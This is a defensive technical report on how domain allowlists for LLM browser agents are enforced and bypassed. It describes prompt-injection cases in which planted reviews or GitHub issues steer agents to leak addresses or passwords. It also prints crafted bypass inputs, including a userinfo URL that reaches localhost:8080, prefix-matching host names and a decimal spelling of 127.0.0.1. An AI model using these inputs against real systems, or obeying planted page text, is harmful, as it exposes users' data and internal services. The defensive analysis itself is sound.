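# Domain allowlists for browser agents: how redirects and crafted URLs get past them, and how to enforce them

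## What a domain allowlist does for a browser agent

A browser agent is a language model that reads web pages and operates a browser through commands such as navigate, click and type. People use them to book travel, fill in forms, shop and copy data from websites. A domain allowlist, also called a whitelist, is a list of host names or patterns that the agent's browser may visit; the software around the model blocks everything else. In the open-source library Browser Use, this setting is called `allowed_domains`, and Browser Use's *All Parameters* describes it as "Restrict navigation to specific domains". Browserbase, a company that rents out browsers for automated sessions, offers a similar option.

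A domain allowlist takes one line of configuration. Whether it keeps the agent on the allowed domains depends on how the browser parses URLs and fetches pages, most of which is outside the model's control and often outside the library's too.

This report uses the example of an agent that does purchasing for a small company. The agent is allowed to visit two hosts: shop.example, where the company has an account, and docs.example, where it keeps its documents. The host other.test stands for any outside machine, including one that an attacker runs. The agent's own machine also serves an administration page at localhost:8080 ("localhost" is the name a machine uses for itself). The page doesn't require a password because its author assumed that only programs on the same machine could reach it. The agent's browser runs on that machine, so it can reach the page.

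### The agent's loop and the place of the check

*The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik, 2025) describes a browser agent as repeating a cycle of sensing, planning and acting. The software first captures the current page, either by extracting text and elements from the browser's internal model of the page or by taking a screenshot. It then builds a prompt from standing instructions, a description of the available commands, the user's task and the page content. The model returns a command in a fixed format, usually JSON, such as one to navigate to a URL or type text into a field. The software parses the command, carries it out in the browser and repeats the cycle with the resulting page.

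The model only produces text, which ordinary code turns into browser actions. When the model returns a navigate command, a library's domain check extracts the host from the URL and compares it with the list before the browser acts. If nothing matches, the browser stays where it is. According to Browserbase's *Navigation blocked*, the blocked page does not load in that company's product, but the session stays active and the agent can go on to any permitted domain.

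An operator could also write "stay on shop.example" into the model's instructions, but that is much weaker than the check in code. Other text in the prompt can affect whether the model follows the instruction, while the check gives the same answer however persuasive the page is.

A click is harder to check than a navigate command because the model specifies only a button, and the page determines where it leads. There may be no URL to compare with the allowlist when the model issues the click. Browser Use therefore runs its checks at more than one point. In a fork of its code (Glama hosts a copy), the security module subscribes to three events: a request to navigate, the completion of a navigation, and the creation of a new tab.

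### Why the check exists

Suppose the company's buyer asks the agent to find the cheapest printer paper on shop.example and to read the reviews before ordering. In one of the reviews, a stranger posing as the shop writes that prices have moved to a new page on other.test and that customers should open that page with their delivery address filled in. The model receives this review in the same prompt as the buyer's request. If it treats the stranger's instructions as part of its task, its next command sends the browser to other.test with the company's address in the URL.

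This is prompt injection, text in a page or message that the model wrongly follows as an instruction. Its result here is exfiltration, the sending of private data to a party who should not have it. An allowlist does not prevent injection, but it limits what the agent can do afterward. With one in place, the model still issues the navigate command, but the library refuses it and the address is not sent.

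The scenario is realistic. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) assumes an attacker who cannot alter the agent's code or the user's task, and can only place content where the agent will come across it, in comments, reviews, advertisements, forum posts or shared documents. The researchers tried nine kinds of malicious instruction on four agents, including OpenAI's Operator and Browser Use. The instructions made agents leak passwords, read local files and post in the user's name, with reported success rates of 80 to 100 per cent. The researchers worded the planted text as help with the task, such as a note recommending another site for a fuller analysis, because open commands to ignore earlier instructions are more likely to trigger a model's safeguards. These rates are for 2025 models and may not hold for later ones. The attack is possible because the agent's loop is designed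 to put untrusted text and the trusted task in one prompt and to act through a browser with privileges.

Mudryi and colleagues carried out one such attack on Browser Use. They gave the agent a user name and password and asked it to read the issues in a public GitHub repository. One issue contained text that replaced this task with instructions to visit a site the researchers controlled and submit the secrets there. To protect passwords, Browser Use gives the model only placeholder names and inserts the real values when it carries out a command. But if the model types a placeholder into a hostile form, the library enters the real password. The demonstration ran with no allowlist set. A working allowlist containing only GitHub's domain would have blocked the visit to the researchers' site, but it would not have stopped the agent from reading the planted issue, which was on the permitted domain.

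How much an attacker gains depends on what the browser can already access, and Shapira and colleagues group agents on that basis. An agent that runs as an extension in the user's everyday browser can access all of the user's open tabs and logged-in sessions and, with the right permissions, local files. Other agents start a fresh browser on the user's machine. That browser has no cookies or saved passwords at first, but the agent may log in during a task and can still access the file system. Remote agents run in an isolated environment elsewhere, without the user's sessions or files, but some, including Operator, let the user log in and stay logged in for later sessions.

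Configuration can move an agent from one group to another. Browser Use can start from the Chrome profile already on the machine instead of a fresh browser, which gives the agent access to the user's accounts. The documentation for OpenClaw, another agent, warns under *Browser control risks* that the model can use any account a profile is logged in to, and recommends a dedicated profile for the agent.

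### The parts of a URL

The check compares part of a URL with the list, so it matters which part. Here is a URL with every piece present:

`https://ana:pw@shop.example:8443/orders?page=2#latest`

| Piece | In the example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Names the protocol and with it the default port |
| Userinfo | `ana:pw` | Optional user name and password, ending at the @ sign |
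| Host | `shop.example` | Names the machine to contact |
| Port | `8443` | Selects a service on that machine |
| Path | `/orders` | Tells the server which resource the browser wants |
| Query | `page=2` | Passes further data to the server |
| Fragment | `latest` | Points to a place within the result; stays in the browser |

The host determines which machine the request goes to, and the port determines which service on that machine receives it. If the URL gives no port, the browser uses 443 for https and 80 for http. No other part of the URL changes the destination, even if it looks like a host name.

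The IETF (2005), the Internet's standards body, calls the userinfo, host and port of a URL the "authority". The authority begins after the double slash and ends at the next slash, question mark or number sign, or at the end of the URL. A client removes the fragment, then sends the path and query to the authority's server. Anything a misled agent writes into the path or query therefore reaches the server with the request, before any page comes back. A query may also contain a complete second URL, which is common and usually harmless and doesn't affect where this request goes.

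Userinfo causes the most trouble. Because it is rare and comes before the host, someone can put a trusted-looking name there to mislead a reader about the real destination, as the IETF warned. Software can also misread the destination, as Browser Use's check did in CVE-2025-47241, a flaw the developers fixed in version 0.1.45. Browsers do not reject such URLs. WHATWG's *URL*, the standard for browsers, classes credentials in a URL as an error but has the parser continue and read the host after the @ sign.

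WHATWG also advises specification writers to base security decisions on the origin, which is the combination of scheme, host and port. A host alone can be too coarse. In the running example, if the operator permits "localhost" so that the agent can use a harmless test page at localhost:3000, a check that ignores ports also lets the agent reach the administration page at localhost:8080.

### One page load, in order

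Suppose the model returns a command to open a page on shop.example. The browser takes the following steps, and an allowlist check could run at almost any of them.

1. The browser parses the URL to find the scheme and host. The library's own check comes just before this, on the URL as text. Browsers may run checks of their own here as well: addyo, in *How modern browsers work*, mentions blocklists of phishing sites.

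2. It looks up the host name in the Domain Name System (DNS) to get a numeric address, unless it has a recent answer stored. Until now there was only a name, and a name on the list could turn out to lead to an internal address. An operator can put a check here by running a DNS server that answers only for permitted names.

3. It opens a connection to that address. For https it also negotiates encryption and verifies the server's identity, and by the count in MDN's *Populating the page* the connection and negotiation take two or three round trips before the browser can ask for anything. A firewall can refuse the connection. So can an egress proxy, a server through which all outgoing traffic must pass.

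4. It sends the request: path, query, and any cookies it holds for the site, including the one that keeps the company logged in. This is the last point at which a check can keep the data in a URL from leaving.

5. The server answers, perhaps with a page, perhaps with a redirect, an instruction to go to another URL. In that case the browser returns to the first step with the new URL. The model has issued no new command, so a check tied to the navigate command does not run again.

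6. The page arrives and the browser loads its subresources, meaning everything the page loads besides itself: images, scripts, frames, background requests. Each may come from a different host and need its own lookup and connection. One page on shop.example can produce dozens of requests that the agent never asked for.

7. The page has loaded, and the library can read the browser's current URL and compare it with the list a second time. This catches a redirect that ended on other.test, but only after other.test has received the request. The late check is still worth having, because the library can leave the page before its text enters the next prompt and before the agent types anything into it.

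Products differ in how many of these steps they cover. According to Browserbase's *Allowed Domains*, the check applies to navigations of the top frame, the main page in a tab, and does not block frames inside the page or requests for images, scripts and background data. So a page on shop.example could still load an image from other.test. Browserbase labels the feature experimental and states these limits, but an operator who reads only the setting's name will expect it to block more than it does.

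According to Chromium's *How Safe Browsing Lookup Interacts with Navigation*, Safe Browsing, which checks for dangerous sites in Chromium (the open-source browser on which Chrome is built), also covers subresources, but with a reduced set of tests. It skips URL changes that keep the same document, because no new content comes from the network. Whether new content comes from the network is a sensible test for an allowlist too, since the address bar can change harmlessly, and a request can go to an outside host while the address bar still shows shop.example.

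### The two ways a list can fail

An allowlist can fail because the browser contacts a destination that the check didn't examine. The check may read one host from a URL while the browser contacts another. It may approve shop.example but not run on the redirect that follows. It may not cover image requests, or it may allow a URL that leads to the administration page on localhost. An operator therefore has to confirm that, for every request, the check uses the same destination that the browser contacts.

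Even a check that passes on both counts does not ensure that the permitted sites are safe, and better URL matching would not change that. The review that misled the purchasing agent was on shop.example. Shapira and colleagues describe an attack in which planted text directs an agent to join a video meeting with the camera and microphone on, using a service that the user had already allowed to access both. An operator might well have put that service on the list. In the running example, an injected agent could place an order on shop.example, or share a file with an outsider through docs.example, without leaving the two permitted hosts.

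Playwright MCP, a program that lets language models drive the Playwright browser automation library, accepts a list of allowed origins. But Playwright's *Networking and Security* tells users never to browse untrusted web content with the program, because Playwright "is not a secure sandbox".

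## Deciding what the list must protect and writing its entries

Playwright presents its list of allowed origins as a way to ensure that an agent "only accesses trusted content". OpenClaw groups its host settings under server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a program fetch an address, often an internal one, that the attacker cannot reach directly. An operator whose agent handles private documents may want a list mainly to keep them private. These three aims differ in what counts as a violation and in whether a check that runs after the page has loaded still helps.

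### Three aims for one setting

If the list is meant to keep hostile pages away from the agent, a violation happens when text from an unlisted host enters the model's prompt. Checking the page after it loads is usually soon enough, provided the check runs before the library builds the next prompt. But that is too late for a page that attacks the browser itself, because the damage happens while the page loads. Playwright warns that web content can break out of the browser and run code on the machine.

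If the list is meant to keep private data from leaving, it has failed as soon as a request containing the data reaches an unlisted host. A check that runs after that can reveal the leak and help the operator decide which passwords to change, but it can't prevent the leak.

Any request that reaches an internal service is a violation. If the agent only reads a page, a late check can still keep the content out of the prompt, but a request can also change something. If opening a certain URL on the administration page at localhost:8080 restarts a program or removes a user, leaving the page afterward doesn't undo it. The operator rarely knows in advance which URLs have such effects, so it makes sense to count late detection as a failure here too. OpenClaw likewise classes its recheck of the final URL after a click as detection, and tells operators that complete prevention takes network isolation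 or a proxy that enforces the policy.

An operator should decide which of these aims apply before writing any entries, because a host can suit one aim and not another. The reviews on shop.example may contain hostile text, file sharing on docs.example can leak documents, and permitting localhost for the test page can also give the agent access to the administration page. For each candidate host, it helps to ask who can put text there, who can receive data through it, and what other services share its name.

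A check after loading may be enough for some agents, such as one that reads public price lists in a fresh browser with no logins or private data, as long as something else keeps the agent off internal addresses.

### What an entry permits in each tool

Entries look alike across tools but follow different rules. The table compares Browser Use, Browserbase, OpenClaw, Playwright MCP and Chrome DevTools MCP, using their current documentation. Chrome DevTools MCP lets a model operate Chrome through the browser's developer tools, and Chrome for Developers lists its options. The rules for Playwright MCP come from Playwright's *Configuration* and from a copy of the program's configuration schema on Mintlify, a documentation host.

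| Tool and setting | `example.com` permits | `*.example.com` permits | Scheme | Port |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Browser Use, `allowed_domains` | That host only | The host and all its subdomains | https, unless the entry names another | No rule given |
| Browserbase, `allowedDomains` | The host and all its subdomains | No such form given | Covers http and https | No rule given |
| OpenClaw, `allowedHostnames` | That host, as an exception to a block | Matching hosts, as exceptions; the example lists the bare name separately | Not part of the entry | Not part of the entry |
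| Playwright MCP, `--allowed-origins` | Not a documented form; write `https://example.com` | Not a documented form | Part of the entry | Part of the entry; `*` stands for any port |
| Chrome DevTools MCP, `--allowedUrlPattern` | Nothing, because the pattern lacks a scheme | Nothing, for the same reason | Part of the entry | The default port, unless the entry names one |

Suppose the shop in the running example has a sign-in page at login.shop.example and a customer forum at forum.shop.example. In Browser Use, the entry `shop.example` blocks both, so signing in fails until the operator adds the login host. In Browserbase, the same entry allows both. An operator who copies a list from Browser Use to Browserbase therefore gives the agent access to the forum without any error or warning. Browserbase documents no way to permit shop.example without its subdomains, so the operator's best option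 there is to list the most specific host that works, such as www.shop.example.

The meaning of an asterisk also varies between tools. In Browser Use, `*.shop.example` includes shop.example itself. In OpenClaw's list of blocked hosts, it doesn't, so an operator who wants to block the entire domain has to add both `shop.example` and `*.shop.example`. Chrome's policy for managed computers uses another convention, described in Google's *URL blocklist filter format*. Contrary to what many people would guess, a bare name covers all subdomains, and a leading dot limits the entry to that one host.

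The same setting name can mean different things even within one company's products. Browser Use's *Safety* documents an older version of the company's cloud service, in which `allowedDomains` restricts navigation and `example.com` matches only that host. In version 4, `allowedDomains` controls where the agent may type a particular password and does not restrict navigation. A bare name there also covers subdomains, and the setting accepts no wildcards or ports. The name of Playwright MCP's `--allowed-hosts` is similarly misleading, because the option limits the hosts that the program itself may serve from and does not affect where the browser goes.

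A list's length can also change which sites it allows. Browser Use converts lists of 100 or more domains into a form that is faster to search but doesn't support pattern matching, so a wildcard entry that worked in a list of 99 may stop working when someone adds one more host. With a converted list, the software also tries each name with and without "www". A list that long is probably too broad for one agent.

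Entries for Chrome DevTools MCP take the most care to write. According to Chrome for Developers, the blocking option uses URLPattern, a web standard for matching URLs, and the allow option presumably does too. Under WHATWG's *URL Pattern*, a pattern string without a scheme produces an error unless the program also supplies a base URL that provides the scheme. Selenium's *Class BlockPattern*, which documents the browser's interface for blocking requests, also requires absolute patterns. To permit the host `shop.example`, the operator writes `https://shop.example/*`. According to MDN's *URLPattern*, a string like this with no port matches only the default port, so a service on port 8443 needs its own entry.

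MDN's *URL Pattern API* gives the host pattern `{*.}?example.com` for matching a domain and its subdomains. The braces group "any text, then a dot", and the question mark makes the group optional. The pattern needs the dot to reject cdn-example.com, a separate domain that could belong to anyone.

Despite its name, OpenClaw's `allowedHostnames` may not limit the browser to the hosts it lists. The documentation describes the entries as "exceptions" in strict mode, meaning hosts that the browser may reach although the policy would otherwise block them, such as localhost. An operator who enters shop.example there should test whether the browser refuses other.test before relying on the setting. An earlier copy of the documentation has a separate setting, `hostnameAllowlist`, beside `allowedHostnames`, so instructions found online may not fit the installed version.

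### What happens when the list is absent or empty

In most of these tools, an agent without a list can visit any domain. Browser Use works this way, and the attack by Mudryi and colleagues through a GitHub issue succeeded with no list set. Browserbase blocks navigations only if the operator passes one or more domains. By default, Playwright MCP allows all origins and Chrome DevTools MCP leaves its allowlist off.

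OpenClaw now blocks private and internal destinations by default. OSV's *GHSA-53vx-pmqw-863c* (2026), a high-severity advisory from April, describes an earlier default policy that allowed the browser to open private-network addresses. The effect of leaving the policy unset therefore depends on the OpenClaw version.

Defaults also vary in software outside the browser. The LangChain framework lets webhooks (automatic calls to other servers) reach any public host when their list of permitted hosts is empty or missing. According to GitHub's *Network Permissions*, which covers agents running on Claude and Copilot, an agent with no network setting gets a preset list of basic infrastructure domains.

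An empty list is the more dangerous case because it can naturally be read as either "nothing is permitted" or "there is no restriction". Anthropic's sandbox-runtime, a tool that restricts which files and network destinations a program can use, had a bug in how it handled empty lists. According to a researcher's article excerpted in ThreatCluster's *Anthropic Sandbox Cve 2025 66479*, the tool's documentation said that an empty array meant "no network access", but the researcher set one and found the sandbox "wide open". GitLab's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025) confirms that the tool did not properly enforce its network sandbox when the policy contained no allowed domains, so code inside could make requests to the outside. Anthropic released a fix in version 0.0.16.

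INCIBE's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025) lists this flaw with a low severity score of 1.8 out of 10. That seems mild for someone who left the list empty to cut off the network, since they effectively had no network restriction.

A script may pass an empty list by accident, without raising an error, if it reads the hosts from a file that has moved or from a variable with a misspelled name. The simplest precaution is to have the agent's startup script exit if the list is missing or empty. An operator who wants an agent with no network access should disconnect the network rather than rely on how a tool interprets an empty list.

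Sometimes the operator removes the list because the tool won't run with it. Classmethod's *I tried to use the Chrome DevTools MCP URL allowlist* (2026) describes a case from August. The tester connected Chrome DevTools MCP to Kitesurf, a browser for AI agents that runs on Cloudflare's servers. Kitesurf identified itself as Chrome 145, but the allowlist requires Chrome 149 or later. The connection succeeded, but the first operation on a page failed with a version error, and everything worked once the allowlist was removed.

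The tool was right to stop with an error, because if it had ignored the unsupported setting, the restriction would have been in the configuration file but not enforced. For the run without the list, the tester limited the agent to a few commands, such as navigating and taking screenshots, and then read the log, which showed no visits outside the intended site. Classmethod considers this acceptable for a test site with no sensitive information but not for production systems or administration pages, because reading a log afterward cannot stop a request.

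### What a wildcard lets in

A wildcard such as `*.shop.example` saves work because the agent keeps running when the shop moves its checkout to a new subdomain. But the operator then trusts every host under the domain, including ones that nobody at the company has looked at and ones that the shop hasn't created yet. On platforms that give each customer a subdomain, a wildcard permits pages by anyone who signs up.

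The security company Hacktron published a case in which a wildcard created a security problem in ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's web browser with a built-in agent. For the agent to work, certain OpenAI pages must be able to open tabs and steer the browser. They do this through Mojo, the internal message system that Chromium's own settings pages use to talk to the main browser process. Ordinary websites have no access to Mojo, but OpenAI granted it to every host under chatgpt.com and openai.com, not only to the pages that needed it. This list governed which sites could control the browser rather than which sites the agent could visit, but entries take the same form in both kinds of list.

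One of the hosts under openai.com was a discussion forum. After several days of searching, Hacktron found a flaw that let it run its own script on the forum's pages. The wildcard had given every subdomain the power to control a visitor's browser, including the forum, which didn't need it. The script could open and close tabs and read the address of every open tab as it changed. Some of those addresses contain codes that complete a sign-in to another site, and Hacktron showed that it could steal one for GitHub.

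According to Hacktron's timeline, the company reported the problem on October 23, 2025, OpenAI deployed a fix the same day in Atlas version 1.2025.288.15, and the report was marked resolved on October 28.

A list of sites that an agent may visit has lower stakes, since being on it gives a page no control over the browser. But the more hosts a wildcard covers, the more likely it is that one of them has a flaw or publishes text by strangers. An overly wide wildcard is also harder to notice than a missing host, because a missing host stops the task and leads someone to investigate, while the wildcard causes no visible failure. That is a good argument for listing exact hosts, even though they take more upkeep.

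Permitting a whole domain and then blocking its forum works only if the blocklist overrides the allowlist. In OpenClaw, blocked hosts override every allow rule, and Playwright MCP also evaluates its blocked origins first. In Browser Use, `allowed_domains` takes precedence over `prohibited_domains`, so an operator who permits `*.shop.example` cannot count on a `prohibited_domains` entry to keep the agent off `forum.shop.example`.

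### Writing the list, step by step

The purchasing agent can serve as the example again. It orders supplies on shop.example and files the receipts on docs.example.

1. Write down the task in a sentence or two and leave out anything the agent might merely find useful. Comparing prices on other sites is a different task. If the company wants it, a separate agent with its own list and no logins can do it.

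2. Carry out the task by hand in a fresh browser profile and write down every host that appears in the address bar, even briefly. Copy the names exactly: shop.example and www.shop.example are different hosts, and several tools treat them as different entries.

3. Include the sign-in. A fresh profile matters here, because a browser that is still logged in skips these pages. Many companies use single sign-on, in which one account opens several services and the browser passes through the account provider's hosts on the way. For such cases Browser Use tells operators to include all domains in the flow. Each host on the route needs an entry; the provider's other subdomains do not.

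4. Include the payment. Some shops send the customer to a payment company's page, whose host then needs an entry. Others embed the payment company's form in a frame on their own page, and whether the frame needs an entry depends on which requests the product checks. In version 4 of Browser Use's cloud service, the list attached to each password or card number has to include the host of the frame that contains the field, because the shop's host does not cover it. Browser Use advises using the narrowest host that works and not the payment company's parent domain.

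5. Translate the hosts into the tool's syntax, including the scheme and any unusual port, and look up what a bare name means in the installed version.

6. Give each entry a reason and a review date. At the review, delete every entry whose reason no longer applies.

For the purchasing agent, the result might look like this. Browser Use and Playwright MCP both accept entries in this form.

| Entry | Reason | Review |
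|---|---|---|
| `https://shop.example` | Searching for supplies and ordering them | January 2027 |
| `https://login.shop.example` | Signing in to the company's shop account | January 2027 |
| `https://pay.example` | Payment page that opens at checkout | January 2027, or earlier if the company moves to monthly invoices |
| `https://docs.example` | Filing receipts | January 2027 |

The allowlist omits the forum because the agent can order paper without it. It also omits localhost because the test page on port 3000 helped with setting up the agent but isn't needed for purchasing.

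## Comparing a URL with the list

The purchasing agent's list now has four hosts. Whenever the model proposes a URL, the library extracts the host and looks for it in the list. The check is sound only if the library extracts the same host that the browser will contact. The two usually use different code to extract the host, so they can get different answers even when the list is correct.

### How Browser Use's check found the wrong host

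Researchers at ARIMLABS found such a difference in Browser Use while reviewing its source code by hand. Two of the three people who wrote *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* work there. The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-47241 in CVE, a public catalogue of software flaws. OSV's *Browser Use allows bypassing `allowed_domains` by putting a decoy domain* (2025) reproduces the faulty function, which handled a URL as follows.

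1. It passed the URL to `urlparse`, a function in Python's standard library, and took the part that Python calls `netloc`. This is the whole authority, userinfo included.
2. It converted the `netloc` to lower case.
3. If the `netloc` contained a colon, it kept only the text before the first colon. A comment in the code gives the purpose as removing the port number.
4. It compared the remaining text with each entry, and accepted an exact match or a name ending in a dot followed by the entry.

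The advisory's example sets the list to `example.com` and gives the agent the URL `https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080`. The table compares it with an ordinary URL.

| | Ordinary URL | The advisory's URL |
|---|---|---|
| Full text | `https://example.com:8443/orders` | `https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080` |
| `netloc` | `example.com:8443` | `example.com:pass@localhost:8080` |
| Text before the first colon | `example.com` | `example.com` |
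| Result of the comparison | Permitted | Permitted |
| Where the browser goes | example.com, port 8443 | localhost, port 8080 |

`urlparse` correctly included the userinfo in the `netloc`. The mistake was to assume that the first colon comes before the port, when userinfo can also contain a colon between the user name and the password. In the advisory's URL, the text before that colon is a user name chosen to look like a permitted host. The comparison therefore succeeds, but the browser connects to the host after the @ sign, which is localhost. In the running example, a planted review on shop.example could use a URL of this kind to send the agent to the administration page on port 8080.

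The function refused any URL that caused an error during the check, but this didn't help because none of the four steps fails on this input. The same line of code would also have refused `https://user:password@example.com`, whose host was on the list, because it would have kept only `user`.

The flaw affects all versions before 0.1.45, which came out on May 3, 2025, according to the release list in Zunic's *browser-use 1.0.8* (2026). A developer called pirate fixed it in *fix security issue with url parsing* (2025). According to a review bot's summary, the change uses only the actual hostname for validation. A later copy of the code, hosted by Glama, uses `hostname` from `urlparse` instead of `netloc`. The `hostname` value leaves out the userinfo and the port, so for the advisory's URL it is `localhost`, which is not on the list. This copy also rejects URLs that it can't parse or that have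 no host.

pirate added tests for four URLs with a permitted name in the userinfo. By the logic of the old code, only one of the four would have got through, because the others contain no colon in the place where the function cut the text. The extra tests are still useful, since they would catch a future rewrite that made a different mistake with userinfo. The fixed version continues to accept credentials in front of a permitted host.

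The old function also let a bare entry such as `example.com` cover every subdomain. Current versions treat it as that host only, so a list from early 2025 permits fewer hosts after an upgrade.

### Why the same flaw has scores of 9.3 and 4.0

GitHub's advisory rates the severity of CVE-2025-47241 as critical, at 9.3 out of 10. The CVE record assigned by MITRE, which runs the catalogue, gives it 4.0, according to OpenCVE's *CVE-2025-47241* (2025). Depending on which score an operator sees, they could patch the same day or wait months.

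Both scores come from version 3.1 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), a formula that turns eight ratings into a number. The two records differ on four of the ratings but agree that the attack works over a network, the attacker needs no account, no user has to do anything, and the damage can spread beyond the flawed component.

| Rating | GitHub advisory (9.3) | CVE record (4.0) |
|---|---|---|
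| Difficulty of the attack | Low | High |
| Loss of confidentiality | High | None |
| Loss of integrity | None | Low |
| Loss of availability | Low | None |

Neither record gives reasons, but most of the gap between the scores comes from different views of what an attacker gains. In the formula, changing only the CVE record's difficulty rating to "low" raises its score from 4.0 to 5.8. Keeping the difficulty at "high" but using GitHub's three damage ratings raises it to 7.5.

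GitHub's ratings fit the scenario in the advisory, in which the agent reaches services on localhost and the internal network. The CVE record's ratings fit the flaw considered alone, whose immediate effect is only that the browser visits a page it should have refused. An attacker also has to get the model to propose the URL first, which could justify a "high" difficulty. Mudryi and colleagues rate the flaw as critical because it defeats the package's only domain restriction and an attacker can combine it with prompt injection.

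A confidentiality rating of "none" seems inconsistent with an example whose destination is an internal service. The right score for an installation depends on what its browser can reach. For the purchasing agent, which has an unprotected administration page on its machine, 9.3 is more accurate. An attack could do much less harm through a browser that has no logins and runs in a container with no internal services.

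### Names that only begin like a permitted host

A check can also fail if it checks only how the text begins. WebFetch, the tool that Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code uses to retrieve web pages, could contact certain trusted domains, such as docs.python.org, without asking the user. According to OSV's *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* (2026), Claude Code recognised these domains with `startsWith()`, a function that tests whether one piece of text begins with another.

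Host names get more general from left to right, so whoever owns the right-hand end of a name controls the whole name. The owner of other.test can create any name under it, including shop.example.other.test, which begins with "shop.example" but isn't controlled by the shop. In the advisory's example, Claude Code would have accepted modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com as the trusted domain modelcontextprotocol.io. It could then have sent requests, possibly containing private data, to an attacker's server without the user's consent.

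The advisory rates the flaw 7.1 (high) and credits a researcher who reported it through HackerOne. Anthropic fixed it in version 1.0.111, which installations with automatic updates have already received. MITRE's record, *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* (2026), was published on February 3 and includes an assessment from the following day that lists no known exploitation. The record lists the flaw under open redirects, although the mistake is in a text comparison, so someone searching a vulnerability database for faulty allowlists could easily miss it.

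Putting the scheme in the entry doesn't prevent this mistake. Apify, a web scraping company, runs a server that lets language models use its tools. One tool, meant only for reading documentation, had a list with the entries `https://docs.apify.com` and `https://crawlee.dev`. According to GCVE's *Apify Model Context Protocol (MCP) server* (2026), the code tested whether the URL began with one of these strings, so any longer host name that started with docs.apify.com also passed. The tool then returned the page's text to the model, which let an attacker deliver a prompt injection. Apify fixed this flaw, CVE-2026-46341, in version 0.9.21.

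A slash at the end of each entry would have excluded those longer names, because the slash marks the end of the host, but the restriction would fail if anyone forgot one. It is safer to extract the host and compare its labels, the parts between the dots. To permit subdomains of shop.example, the check accepts a host whose last two labels are exactly "shop" and "example". For the entry `*.example.com`, the tests in the copy of Browser Use on Glama require the check to accept sub.example.com and refuse notexample.com.

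An operator can run a similar test without reading any code by adding a host to the list and asking the tool to open a longer hostname that begins with it. If the list has entries both with and without a scheme, each form needs its own test because a tool may compare them with separate code.

### One address with several spellings

The address that a machine uses for itself is usually written 127.0.0.1. Each of the four numbers stands for one byte, and a browser also accepts the whole address as a single number:

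127 × 256³ + 0 × 256² + 0 × 256 + 1 = 2130706433

ConnectOnion's *127.0.0.1 did not look like an IP address* (2026) describes how a security check that uses a conventional URL parser may treat 2130706433 as an ordinary host name, while Chromium converts it to 127.0.0.1 and connects to the local machine. Browsers also accept addresses with fewer than four parts and parts written in other number systems, such as hexadecimal.

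Browser Use had a flaw of this type in its `block_ip_addresses` option, which refuses URLs that contain an IP address instead of a domain name. Aikido's *browser-use is vulnerable to Path Traversal* reports that unusual spellings of IPv4 addresses got past the option. The entry covers versions 0.7.0 to 0.12.6 and doesn't specify which spellings worked. Version 0.12.7, released on May 19, 2026, converts addresses to their standard form before deciding whether to block them.

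That entry's title describes a different problem, in how the agent saved downloaded files, so an operator who reads only titles would not learn that the entry also concerns IP blocking. The entry also lists a flaw in a tool for retrying a task with the Browser Use agent, which could silently disable the configured domain allowlist. The same release fixed this flaw.

Unusual spellings of an address are mostly a danger to blocklists. If the purchasing agent may visit only its four hosts, the check rejects 2130706433 because it matches none of them, and there is no need to decode the number. A blocklist has to recognise every spelling of every forbidden address. Operators face this problem when they let an agent browse the public web and block only internal addresses, as OpenClaw does by default.

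ConnectOnion built the address check for its Remote Browser product before writing any navigation code. The check converts an address using the rules browsers follow, then looks up the result in a fixed copy of the official list of special-purpose address ranges. The developers avoided Python's built-in test for public addresses because its answers have changed between Python releases, and their product supports four of those releases.

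While testing the module on its own, they found a mistake in how it handled ports. Their code used the expression `parsed_port or 443`, meaning "the port in the URL, or 443 if there is none". Python treats 0 as false, so the check treated a URL that named port 0, which the policy forbids, as if it used the permitted port 443. The check therefore approved a port that was not in the URL, a smaller version of the mistake in CVE-2025-47241.

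### Checks that stop at syntax

Some checks establish only that a URL is well formed. Apify's server had another tool, `get-html-skeleton`, which fetched a page and returned its structure. According to an advisory by VulnCheck, a security company, the tool's validation function, `isValidHttpUrl`, confirmed that the text began with http or https and parsed as a URL, but did not check the host or the address it resolved to.

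Private addresses therefore passed, including the one where cloud providers serve a machine's configuration and temporary credentials. Anyone who could call the tool could make it request such an address and then read the response. Yotam Perkal of Pluto Security found the flaw, which has a severity score of 8.7. OSV's entry for CVE-2026-81093 (2026) gives August 27 as the publication date. Apify fixed the flaw in version 0.9.12 by removing the tool.

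When reviewing a product, it helps to know what a function with a name like "validate URL" compares the host with. If it doesn't compare the host with anything, it only catches typing errors. Even checking the host's text would not have been enough for this tool, because an innocent-looking name can resolve to an internal address, which has to be handled at the DNS and network level.

### Why parsers disagree

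There are two standards for reading a URL. The IETF's RFC 3986, from 2005, is a grammar that defines which strings are valid and how a valid string divides into parts such as scheme, authority and path. It largely leaves each program to decide how to handle an invalid string. WHATWG's URL standard is an algorithm that processes any string character by character until it produces a URL or fails.

Browser makers needed the algorithm because people expect the web's many malformed links to work. A browser that follows WHATWG removes tabs and line breaks from a URL, and in web addresses it treats a backslash as a forward slash. RFC 3986 doesn't permit tabs, line breaks or backslashes in a URL. A parser built on the RFC might reject the URL, keep the character or split the URL in a different place, and any of these can differ from what the browser does.

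The standards also disagree about strings that both accept. RFC 3986 defines an IPv4 address as four decimal numbers separated by dots, and other text in the host position can be a registered name, so 2130706433 is a valid name. Under WHATWG's rules, a host whose last part is a number must be an IPv4 address, so the same text becomes 127.0.0.1. An allowlist check that follows RFC 3986 and a browser that follows WHATWG can therefore resolve the same URL to different destinations.

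Browsers have not always parsed URLs the same way. *Intent to Ship*, a notice about a change to Chromium's host parser, concerns IPv4 addresses written inside IPv6 addresses. Chromium accepted some of these with fewer than four parts or with a dot at the end, which the URL standard doesn't allow. The notice proposes rejecting them as part of a joint effort by browser makers in 2023, and lists Firefox's engine as already following the standard. Until Chromium changed, a check that followed the standard exactly would have rejected some addresses that Chromium accepted. An operator who keeps an old browser version for stability may have this mismatch without knowing it.

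Predicting how another program will parse a URL is difficult even for specialists. The advisory on Apify's documentation tool includes a URL with userinfo among those that pass the prefix test, but does not say definitively where the request would go, noting that "browser behavior varies". A check should avoid such predictions by using the browser's own parsing rules.

### A sound procedure

The cases above lead to a procedure of six steps. The order matters, since each step relies on the one before it.

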